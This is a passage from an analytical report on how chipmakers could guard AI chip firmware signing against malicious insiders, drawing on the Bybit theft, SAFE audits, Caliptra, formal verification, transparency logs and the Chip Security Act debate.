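The February 2025 theft from the cryptocurrency exchange Bybit shows how little extra approvers help when they all rely on the same information. Bybit lost about $1.5 billion from a wallet that required several people to sign each transfer. According to NCC Group's *In Depth Technical Analysis of the Bybit Hack*, at least three authorised signers approved what looked like a routine internal transfer but in fact gave the attackers control of the wallet.

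The signers reviewed transfers on a website called Safe{Wallet}, and the attackers had inserted malicious code into it. The site displayed the correct address and transaction details but sent different data to the signers' hardware devices. Bybit's chief executive, Ben Zhou, signed last. CertiK's *Bybit Incident Technical Analysis* reports his account that every signer saw the same false display at Safe{Wallet}'s real web address. The Block's *Lazarus appears to compromise Safe developer machine* reports that investigators traced the attack to the wallet supplier's cloud systems and had found no break-in at Bybit itself.

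None of the three signers had to be malicious or even unusually careless. In the formula, *c* was close to 100%, because anything that fooled one signer would fool the others. A fourth signer using the same website would probably have approved too.

Trail of Bits' *How Threat Modeling Could Have Prevented the $1.5B Bybit Hack* (2025) recommends that signers check each transaction with a separate program on a separate, secure computer, and compare the resulting hash byte by byte with the one on the signing device. Firmware approvers should do the same, because an insider who controls the approval screen could display the hash of version 4.2 while sending a different hash to the signing module.

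Computing the hash on separate computers catches cases where the approvers see one thing and sign another, as at Bybit, where the intended transfer and the signed one had different hashes. It doesn't help if an insider has planted code in version 4.2 itself, because the hashes will match and both approvers can sign the firmware with the backdoor in it.

### Arguments for and against dual control

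Dual control prevents a lone signer from bypassing code review, independent builds and testing, which no earlier check can do. The signer has to persuade a colleague or get the malicious code through the official process, where planting it leaves a commit, a changed script or some other trace that colleagues may find.

A privately signed file is also especially hard to discover, because the insider can give it to one smuggler and no other customer or researcher ever sees it. Code in an official release goes to everyone, and somebody may eventually analyze it. Preventing private signing is therefore more valuable than it would seem from counting the attacks it blocks.

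Dual control also protects against honest mistakes and stolen passwords. An engineer might submit a test build that leaves out the licence check, and a second person may notice the wrong file name. An outsider who takes over one approver's account still needs another. If something goes wrong, investigators can identify both approvers from the log, provided the log is genuine, and ask them what they saw. The prospect of being questioned may deter some insiders and make others more careful.

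The main objection to dual control is that it can create false confidence. A regulator who hears that two people approved every release may assume that both examined it. Each approver may also reasonably assume that the other has checked the details, or that the reviewers did so weeks ago, so both may sign without examining the release.

Delay is a smaller objection. NIST tells organisations to consider the risks of dual authorisation when public safety requires an immediate response. A chipmaker may need to fix a serious vulnerability on a Sunday night, but it can keep several approvers on call. Letting one person sign in an emergency would be more dangerous, because an insider could wait for an emergency or invent one. The Air Force allows exceptions to its two-person rule when people or a weapon face an immediate threat, but it does not count exercises as emergencies.

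Both objections are reasons to design the process carefully, not to abandon it. Every official release must pass through the signing session, so a company can require other evidence there. Refusing to sign until the two builds match is a much stronger rule than requiring two people to approve, and the company needs control of the key to enforce it.

### What approvers would have to check

Multi-person approval works best when the approvers can understand what they are signing. Petrie suggests that several regulators sign each licence, which is short enough for each of them to read in full and compare with the application. Approvers of a firmware binary have to rely on indirect evidence, because the binary may contain millions of machine instructions.

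The table sets out what that evidence could be. The costs are rough estimates, and each check covers something that the others miss.

| Check before approval | What it could catch | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| Compute the hash on a separate computer and compare it with the release record | A different file substituted at signing | Minutes per release |
| Verify the signed provenance | A build from the wrong source or with the wrong settings | Very little once automated |
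| Compare the file with an independent build | Tampering on one of the build systems | A second build system with its own administrators, and the work of making builds reproducible |
| Read every source change since the last release | Some of the malicious code in those changes | Days or weeks of skilled work per release |
| Test or formally verify the licence check against a written rule | Flaws in the licence check itself | Perhaps weeks at first, then much less per release |

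The first three checks show that the file came from the approved source. Only the last two cover what the code does, and of those, reading the code takes far longer to repeat. If a release changes 10,000 lines and an approver can carefully read 200 lines an hour, each approver would need 50 hours. That is more than a working week, and most people would start to skim under that pressure.

A separate licence-check module of 500 lines would take each approver two and a half hours to read at the same speed. They could read the whole module before every release, including unchanged code, and might notice a flaw that somebody had assembled from several harmless-looking commits. They could still miss flaws, though, and the rest of the firmware would remain unread.

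Finding suitable approvers may be harder than finding the time. The engineers who understand the licence check best probably wrote it, and they should not approve their own work. Staff who look after the signing keys are more independent but may not be able to read firmware. An engineer from another firmware team could be a good compromise, as long as the two teams do not routinely approve each other's releases as a favour.

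The company also has to decide whether both approvers should make the same checks. If one reads the code for the licence check while the other compares the builds, they can check more in the same time, but one malicious or careless person is then enough to defeat either check. If both do everything, each check has a backup but takes twice the work. Software can compare hashes and verify provenance without the lapses in attention that people have, so it makes sense to automate those checks and have both approvers concentrate on the code.

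Cooper and colleagues describe a signing system that inspects the code, approvals and metadata, and signs only if the package meets all requirements. A chipmaker could add matching builds and a passed licence test to those requirements, so that even two approvers acting together could not skip them. Anyone who can edit the requirements would then have as much power as a signer, so any change to them should also need two people's approval.

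## Independent checks on AI chip firmware before and after signing

A signing system can refuse any release without proof of inspection, but someone still has to inspect each one. Several existing checks could supply that proof, and a few others can limit the damage if a bad release is signed.

### Two reviewers for every change

The SLSA guidelines have levels for source code as well as for builds. According to SLSA's *Requirements for producing source*, at source Level 4 the system that stores the code requires two trusted people to review every change to a protected branch. A protected branch is a copy of the code that the company has marked as important, such as the one it uses to build releases.

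Requiring two people to review each change stops a malicious maintainer from merging code that nobody else has read, as Jia Tan did with the xz test files. It also forces a malicious developer to get every change past a colleague. It does not stop a malicious build engineer, and two honest reviewers can still miss a subtle flaw. If a company counts the author as one of the two, only one other person reads the code.

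A review rule covers only code submitted for review, and an engineer could compile an unreviewed version on a laptop. Google has addressed this in its own data centres, where a system called Borg assigns programs to servers. Google's *Binary Authorization for Borg*, last updated in May 2024, describes an enforcement check on every Borg service, which ensures that people have reviewed and approved software before Google deploys it, particularly software that can access sensitive data. Google presents the check as protection against insiders, such as an engineer who uses legitimate access to the servers to start a private program that copies users' data.

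Google can enforce this where the program runs because it owns the servers. A chip in a customer's data centre checks only a signature, which contains no record of who reviewed the code, so a chipmaker would have to enforce the rule at signing, by having the signing system look up the reviews for every commit in the release. It could also design its chips to require a second signature from a separate service that signs only reviewed builds. A signer with a private version of the firmware could then not get the chips to run it. But whoever administers the review records could still mark an unread change as approved, so administering them needs two people as well.

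### Outside audits tied to a hash

Reviewers who work for the chipmaker share its deadlines and its managers. The Open Compute Project (OCP), through which data-centre operators and their suppliers share hardware designs, started a programme in 2023 to bring in outsiders. Until then, cloud providers had commissioned their own audits of suppliers' firmware, and the results usually stayed with the provider that asked for them, according to *OCP-SAFE, a systematic hardware security appraisal framework* (Bryankel, 2023), a post on Microsoft's Azure blog. Open Compute Project's *Security Appraisal Framework and Enablement* (2023), or SAFE, lets many customers rely on one audit:

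1. The manufacturer chooses an approved reviewer, and the two agree on what the review will cover.
2. The reviewer examines the design and reads the source code, mostly by hand.
3. The manufacturer fixes the problems, and the reviewer checks the fixes.
4. The reviewer signs a short report that identifies the firmware by its hash and lists the vulnerabilities.
5. To claim SAFE endorsement, the manufacturer must have that report published.

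The approvers at signing can use the hash to look for a report on the exact file they are asked to approve. A customer can later check the hash in the chip's attestation against the published reports. A private version made for a smuggler would have no report, but the smuggler would have no reason to object, so a regulator would have to make the comparison.

Even the most basic review looks for several flaws an insider might plant, including passwords and keys written into the code, debugging access left in the finished product, and mistakes in checking input. Reviewers also list sensitive functions such as remote control, which should include a way to shut the chip down. More demanding reviews also examine the boundaries between components and resistance to physical attack.

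*OCP S.A.F.E. How-to* (Kondziela, Dragusin and Anderson, 2025) explains that nobody passes or fails a SAFE review. A signed report therefore doesn't certify that firmware is safe, and an approver has to read it, not just confirm that it exists. All three write for NCC Group, a security company that performs these reviews. The manufacturer decides whether anything appears in public, and can hold back findings while it works on a fix, typically for up to 90 days.

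The review could also miss planted code in two other ways. The reviewer mostly reads source code, but the hash in the report identifies a binary. Unless the reviewer also builds that binary, it could contain a build engineer's change that isn't in the source. The framework also requires a review of every production version, but the reviewer concentrates on what has changed in each one, and so could miss a flaw that somebody assembled from harmless-looking changes over several releases.

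For a published audit of Caliptra, an open-source security component for chips, NCC Group (2023) assigned two consultants for a total of 30 person-days. When they returned in October to check the fixes, they found one new problem, which the developers corrected within days. The first inspection may have missed it, or one of the fixes may have introduced it. An audit like this involves far more expert time than an ordinary code review, but it does not guarantee that no problems remain.

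The framework bars reviewers from belonging to a company they audit or having ties to firms that sell vulnerabilities. Reviewers can lose their approval for serious lapses, such as endorsing firmware that contains a hard-coded password. But the manufacturer still chooses the reviewer, so a reviewer who wants repeat business has some reason to be lenient.

Microsoft has apparently gone further for UEFI firmware, which starts most PCs and servers. According to the audit company ivision, firmware makers who want Microsoft's signature must now have a SAFE review every year. This is close to what governance firmware needs, because the company that holds the signing key requires an outside inspection. But an annual review would still miss releases made between reviews, and an insider could wait until after a review to plant malicious code.

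### Open designs for the root of trust

Comparing a chip's attestation with an audit report is useful only if the attestation is true. The attestation comes from the root of trust, the small piece of hardware and permanent code that starts first and that every later check depends on. An insider who weakened the root of trust could cause a chip to produce an attestation for audited firmware while running different firmware.

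CHIPS Alliance's *Caliptra* (2025) describes a version of this component that designers can build into GPUs, processors and storage drives. Its hardware design and firmware are public, so outsiders can inspect them, and anyone can contribute. The founding companies, AMD, Google, Microsoft and Nvidia, settle major technical questions by a three-quarters vote, so no single founder should be able to force through a change.

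The CHIPS Alliance specification requires the chip to measure its startup code and configuration, in practice by hashing them, and to give the results to Caliptra, an open-source root of trust. Caliptra stores the results and reports them in signed attestations. *Technical Options for Flexible Hardware-Enabled Guarantees* (Petrie and Aarne, 2025) suggests OpenTitan, another open-source root of trust, as a possible starting point for a security processor that outsiders could trust.

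To plant a flaw in one of these designs, an insider would have to do so in public, where engineers from rival companies could see it. The xz attack shows that public code can still hide a backdoor, but Caliptra gets far more professional scrutiny than xz did as Collin's hobby project. The rest of the chip's firmware doesn't get this public scrutiny, and Caliptra would still correctly attest to an official release that contained a backdoor.

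A public design does not prove that the factory followed it, either. Petrie and Aarne propose comparing the design with physical scans of randomly selected chips, which would also help against an insider in manufacturing.

### Proving what a licence check does

Formal verification can rule out classes of flaws in a small piece of governance firmware if someone first writes down exactly what the code should do.

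In Petrie's design, a licence contains a device number *d*, a licence number *n*, an allowance *a* and a signature *s*. Let *D* be the chip's own device number, *N* the largest licence number it has used, and *M* the largest reasonable allowance. The rule is that the chip accepts a licence if and only if:

*d* = *D*, *n* > *N*, 0 < *a* ≤ *M*, and *s* is valid under the regulator's public key

A hidden exemption that let a smuggler's chips accept a licence that fails one of the conditions would violate the "only if", which protects the regulator. A hidden command that made a chip refuse valid licences would violate the "if", which protects the owner. If someone had changed the `>` to `>=`, a verification tool could report the case *n* = *N* as a counterexample.

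The team would need a second rule that after accepting a licence, the chip must set *N* to *n* and add *a* to the usage meter, and that it must do no computing when the meter is at zero. Without this rule, the check could accept the right licences and then fail to record them.

A location check needs different rules, because the landmark server does the timing. The chip's firmware must sign only fresh requests meant for that chip and never leak the chip's identity key, which means that nothing the chip sends out, apart from its signatures, may depend on the key. Proving this is harder than verifying a comparison of two numbers, but researchers have proved similar properties for larger programs.

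The best-known example is seL4, the core of an operating system. Enyedi (2026), in *Human-Certified Module Repositories for the AI Age*, says it has roughly 10,000 lines of C and a computer-checked proof that extends to the binary. A licence check should be much smaller. Enyedi also warns that such proofs take a lot of work and do not scale to whole collections of software. A chipmaker could therefore probably verify the licence check but not all the firmware around it.

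A proof about the source code stops a malicious developer from weakening the check, but a build engineer can still alter the binary. A proof about the binary protects against both, if someone outside the build team checks the proof against the exact file awaiting signature. An insider who writes the rule could still put "*n* ≥ *N*" into it, and the tool would then correctly prove that the flawed code obeys the rule. Flaws elsewhere in the firmware could also defeat the verified check.

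### Public logs of signed firmware

An insider who signs a private version of the firmware will not submit it to an auditor or a verification team. A transparency log, a public list of releases that people can add to but not delete from, makes such a version hard to keep secret. This works only if chips refuse any firmware that is not on the list.

A chip can check that a release is on the list without downloading the whole list. The log can arrange its entries in a tree, hashing them in pairs, then hashing the results in pairs, until a single hash represents every entry. Proving that one release is among *n* entries takes about log₂ *n* hashes, or 20 for a million entries. The chip recomputes the final hash from the release and those 20 hashes, then checks the log's signature on it. A smuggled private version would have to appear on the public list before it could run, and the chipmaker's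 staff could notice that it matched no planned release.

Planted code in an official release would look normal in the log, but the log may help investigators afterwards. *Software Distribution Transparency and Auditability* (2017) considers a maintainer who puts a backdoor into a source package. The archive accepts the package only with the maintainer's signature, so the logged files would show whose key signed it. The researchers tested their system on two years of software updates.

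The log's operator could also cheat by showing one chip a list that includes the malicious release and everyone else a list without it. Observers normally catch this by comparing the lists they receive. *Contour* (2017) points out that an attacker who controls the victim's network connection can block the comparison, and that a malicious update, once running, can disable the comparison software. It proposes using Bitcoin's public ledger so that devices can reject such an update before installing it. The same concern applies to AI chips, since a smuggler controls the network around a smuggled chip. The root of trust should therefore check the log entry before the new firmware runs.

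### What Nvidia, AMD and Google use now

Public evidence about AI accelerators is patchy, and none of the three companies appears to have published a process that combines all these checks.

AMD has the clearest link to outside audits. In October 2023, Bryankel described AMD as one of the first companies to prototype publishing a short SAFE report, for its MI300X GPUs. That does not show whether every firmware release since then was reviewed.

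Nvidia's Hopper and Blackwell GPUs have a root of trust, the Foundation Security Processor. It starts from permanent code inside the GPU and must establish trust before any other firmware may run, according to the Linux kernel documentation's *FSP (Foundation Security Processor) and Secure Boot*. Petrie and Aarne report that the security logic on Nvidia's on-chip controllers appears to be formally verified. If so, Nvidia already has people who could verify a licence or location check, though each check would need its own rules and proof.

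Google's Binary Authorization covers services on Borg, which do not include the firmware inside a chip. It therefore does not show how Google reviews firmware for its own AI accelerators, called TPUs. Nvidia and AMD do not seem to have published a comparable two-person rule for firmware.

All three companies help steer Caliptra. Dark Reading's *Chip Giants Finalize Spec to Bake Security Into Silicon* (2024) reported that chips containing it would start reaching the market in 2026. Development continues, and CHIPS Alliance (2026) listed speakers from AMD, Google and Nvidia for an October conference, with one talk on more thorough testing of version 2.2. It is less clear which AI accelerators on sale today contain Caliptra.

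Buyers can at least ask for these protections in standard terms. OCP published its S.O.L.I.D. requirements in January 2026. Semiconductor Engineering's *How OCP S.O.L.I.D. Completes The Data Center Security Picture* describes them and also promotes an auditing service. For accelerators, the requirements include rollback protection and a root of trust that measures the firmware for attestation. SAFE reviewers can check a product against them.

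Transparency logs seem furthest from use in AI chips. At the October conference, speakers from Microsoft and KonaSense were due to present a log that extends SAFE reports, but their example was firmware for the controller that manages a server. They proposed logging each component of that firmware separately, so that an operator could check or update one without re-signing the whole file.

### FlexHEG's answer: open code and several approvers

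The flexHEG proposal would put a guarantee processor between each AI chip and the outside world. Petrie and Aarne's design goals rule out backdoors for secret surveillance or control, and intentional flaws that would let insiders get around the system's rules. A third goal is to let outsiders verify that the system works as expected. The processor's design and the code that enforces the rules would be open source.

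Petrie and Aarne also suggest using three guarantee processors from different manufacturers and following the majority when the processors disagree. A single dishonest manufacturer then could not relax a rule, but Petrie and Aarne acknowledge that more processors may give a compromised one more chance to sabotage the chip. If all three processors ran the same flawed firmware, they would all give the same wrong answer.

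Updates would need approval from *k* of *n* named parties, which could be companies, regulators or states. In Petrie and Aarne's pseudocode, the processor hashes the update and checks the signatures, ignoring unknown signers and repeated names. It accepts the update once it has counted *k* valid signatures.

Requiring signatures from several organisations is much safer than requiring them from two colleagues at one company, because an attacker would have to successfully bribe or threaten several organisations with different interests. But if the organisations sign whatever the developers send them, five signatures protect against a planted flaw no better than one.

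The table shows how inspection changes the chance that a planted flaw is approved. It assumes that each approver has an independent chance of spotting the flaw, and that anyone who spots it refuses to sign but does not warn the others.

| Chance that an approver spots the flaw | One approver | Any three of five | All five |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0% (nobody inspects the code) | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| 20% | 80% | 94% | 33% |
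| 50% | 50% | 50% | 3% |
| 80% | 20% | 6% | 0.03% |

Requiring three of five signatures can be worse than relying on one approver who inspects the code. If each signer has a 20% chance of detecting a flaw, at least three of the five will probably miss it, and their signatures are enough to approve the update. Requiring all five signatures is much more likely to stop the flaw, but it also lets any one signer block every update, including urgent fixes.

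Open code can avoid this trade-off, because anyone who finds the flaw can show it to everyone else. Three-of-five approval then becomes almost as safe as unanimous approval, as long as the finder reports the flaw before the vote. But when the approvers are states, an intelligence service that discovers a hidden exemption might prefer to keep quiet, sign the update and use the exemption itself.

An update can also change who approves later updates. Petrie and Aarne allow this so that the system can adapt, but it makes the list of signers a very attractive target. Their pseudocode ignores a repeated name but does not check for a repeated key. If an insider got the same public key onto the list under two names, whoever held that key would count as two approvers. The pseudocode is short and is not finished firmware, but it shows how little an insider would need to change. Petrie and Aarne suggest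 stricter approval for more important updates. A change to the list of signers should be in the strictest group, in a release that contains nothing else.

### After a bad release gets out

Suppose release 41 of a chip's firmware contains a hidden exemption in the licence check, and researchers discover it six months later. The chipmaker signs a corrected release, 42. Release 41 still has a valid signature, and as Petrie notes, any chip whose rollback counter allows that release can keep using it. A chip with its counter at 40 accepts both releases until the counter is raised to 41, after which it accepts only 42 and later versions.

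A staged release can limit some kinds of damage. The chipmaker might send new firmware to 1% of chips, wait two weeks, and continue only if nothing goes wrong. This works well against code that crashes chips or steals data from ordinary customers, who may notice, but it works badly against the exemption because the signed file is the same for every chip. A smuggler who gets a copy from the first 1% can install it on any compatible chip whose counter allows it, even if the chipmaker cancels the rest of the release.

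The chipmaker also has to decide when to raise the counter. Raising it as soon as a chip installs the new release prevents the owner from going back if the release turns out to be bad. NVIDIA's *Secure AI Compatibility Matrix* rules out a return to Hopper firmware 1.7.1 or earlier for customers who use Secure AI features with version 1.8.0 or later. If such a release had a backdoor, the fix would need a higher version number, as with Debian's renumbered xz package. For routine updates, it may be better to wait until the staged release is complete before raising the counter, but when an update fixes a known backdoor, waiting only gives attackers more time to use the backdoor.

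Chipmakers have other tools besides version counters. The Open Compute Project's guidance on secure boot requires a way to revoke firmware that the manufacturer has already signed. Revoking the signing key is more drastic because it can invalidate every release signed with that key, and the chipmaker would then have to re-sign the good ones with a new key.

Attestation can then show which chips are safe. Petrie recommends that the attestation report include the counter's value as well as the release number, because the owner of a chip running release 42 could reinstall 41 the next day if the counter is still at 40. The root of trust should produce this report and control the counter, since a backdoored release could misreport its own version or falsely report that it had raised the counter.

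All this assumes that the owner wants the fix, but an owner who profits from the exemption does not. Petrie and Aarne propose that each licence state a minimum firmware version, so that a chip running older firmware stops working. With three-month licences, an owner could delay the update for up to three months. Petrie and colleagues propose a similar rule for flexHEG, in which the guarantee processor would block the chip unless an update is installed regularly, for example every three months.

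These rules work against most flaws, but they may fail against a flaw in the licence check itself. If release 41 lets a chip reuse its last licence forever, the chip never needs a new licence with a higher minimum version, so the licence check no longer forces it to update. A deadline would still work only if a separate component enforced it, such as a root of trust that blocks any release from starting after a fixed date.

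Otherwise, chip owners need some outside pressure to install the update. Petrie suggests making it a condition of the warranty, or of keeping favourable treatment in future export decisions. A cloud company that plans to buy more chips would probably comply, but a smuggler has no warranty to lose, so inspectors may have to find the smuggled chips.

Deadlines create new risks. *International Security Applications of Flexible Hardware-Enabled Guarantees* (2025) warns that if the approvers cannot agree on the next update, every device could lock down. An approver might also publicly agree to a stricter update but secretly sign an extension for the old firmware, then keep using it in some of its own data centres. If there are only three approvers and two can decide, those two can make demands of the third.

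The suggested defences are attestation of the firmware version, rollback protection, and a design that prevents approvers from secretly authorising two versions at once. The last would be especially useful because secret signatures are hard to rule out. Petrie and Aarne observe that a signature proves a party signed an update, but proving that the party did not sign would probably require evidence from every device that holds its key.

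One protection against a lockdown is a basic version of the rules that nobody can revoke, perhaps one that lets chips run at reduced speed, so that owners always keep some use of their chips. But Petrie and Aarne acknowledge that nobody could fix a vulnerability in that version without the owner's cooperation. If an insider planted a flaw there, it would be especially hard to remove.

### The dispute over built-in controls

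Nvidia argues that governments should not require controls that can disable a chip. In *No Backdoors. No Kill Switches. No Spyware*, it writes that kill switches and built-in backdoors "create single points of failure" and would help hackers. Its main historical example is the Clipper chip of 1993, an encryption device with built-in access for the US government.

The Center for Cybersecurity Policy and Law extends this argument to the location checks in the Chip Security Act. An attacker who found a vulnerability in the checks might learn where sensitive government or military chips are, or exploit the checks to gain access and disable the chips. The Center also notes that the Senate bill orders a study of ways to change how illegally acquired chips function, which could lead to a kill switch.

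Supporters reply that the bill requires no kill switch. The Center for AI Safety Action Fund's *The Chip Security Act* explains that timed checks would locate a chip to within about 50 miles, need only a software update, and be unable to slow or stop the chip. The group overstates its case when it writes that the bill "explicitly forbids" kill switches. The quoted text only bars interpreting the bill as requiring them, so a manufacturer could still build one voluntarily.

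Insider risk strengthens Nvidia's case against a kill switch that halts chips, because planted code could trigger it. But Nvidia's GPUs already depend on firmware that Nvidia signs, so a malicious release could probably disable many of them even without a kill switch. That makes Nvidia's signing process close to a single point of failure. Leaving out the kill switch makes an insider's work harder but doesn't remove the danger. Independent validation and several layers of protection, which Nvidia itself recommends, are needed either way.

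Other parts of Nvidia's argument would hold even if every employee were honest. Foreign customers may refuse to buy chips that the US government can switch off, however well Nvidia guards the switch. The Clipper chip's best-known failure was a major design flaw that an AT&T researcher found in 1994, not the work of an insider.

The supporters' assurances are more vulnerable to insiders than the supporters acknowledge. An employee could add a kill switch even if the law does not require one. The claim that location software could not affect a chip's operation describes the software as designed. A malicious developer could make that claim false unless the hardware blocks the software from the controls for power, clock speed and memory. The supporters also say the software would be transparent, but customers could rely on that only after inspecting the code and matching it to the binary. Insider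 risk does not affect the supporters' arguments about cost, exports and technical feasibility.

Both sides focus on harm to the chip's owner and say little about an insider who helps the owner cheat, for example by making the firmware leak the identity key that the location checks depend on.
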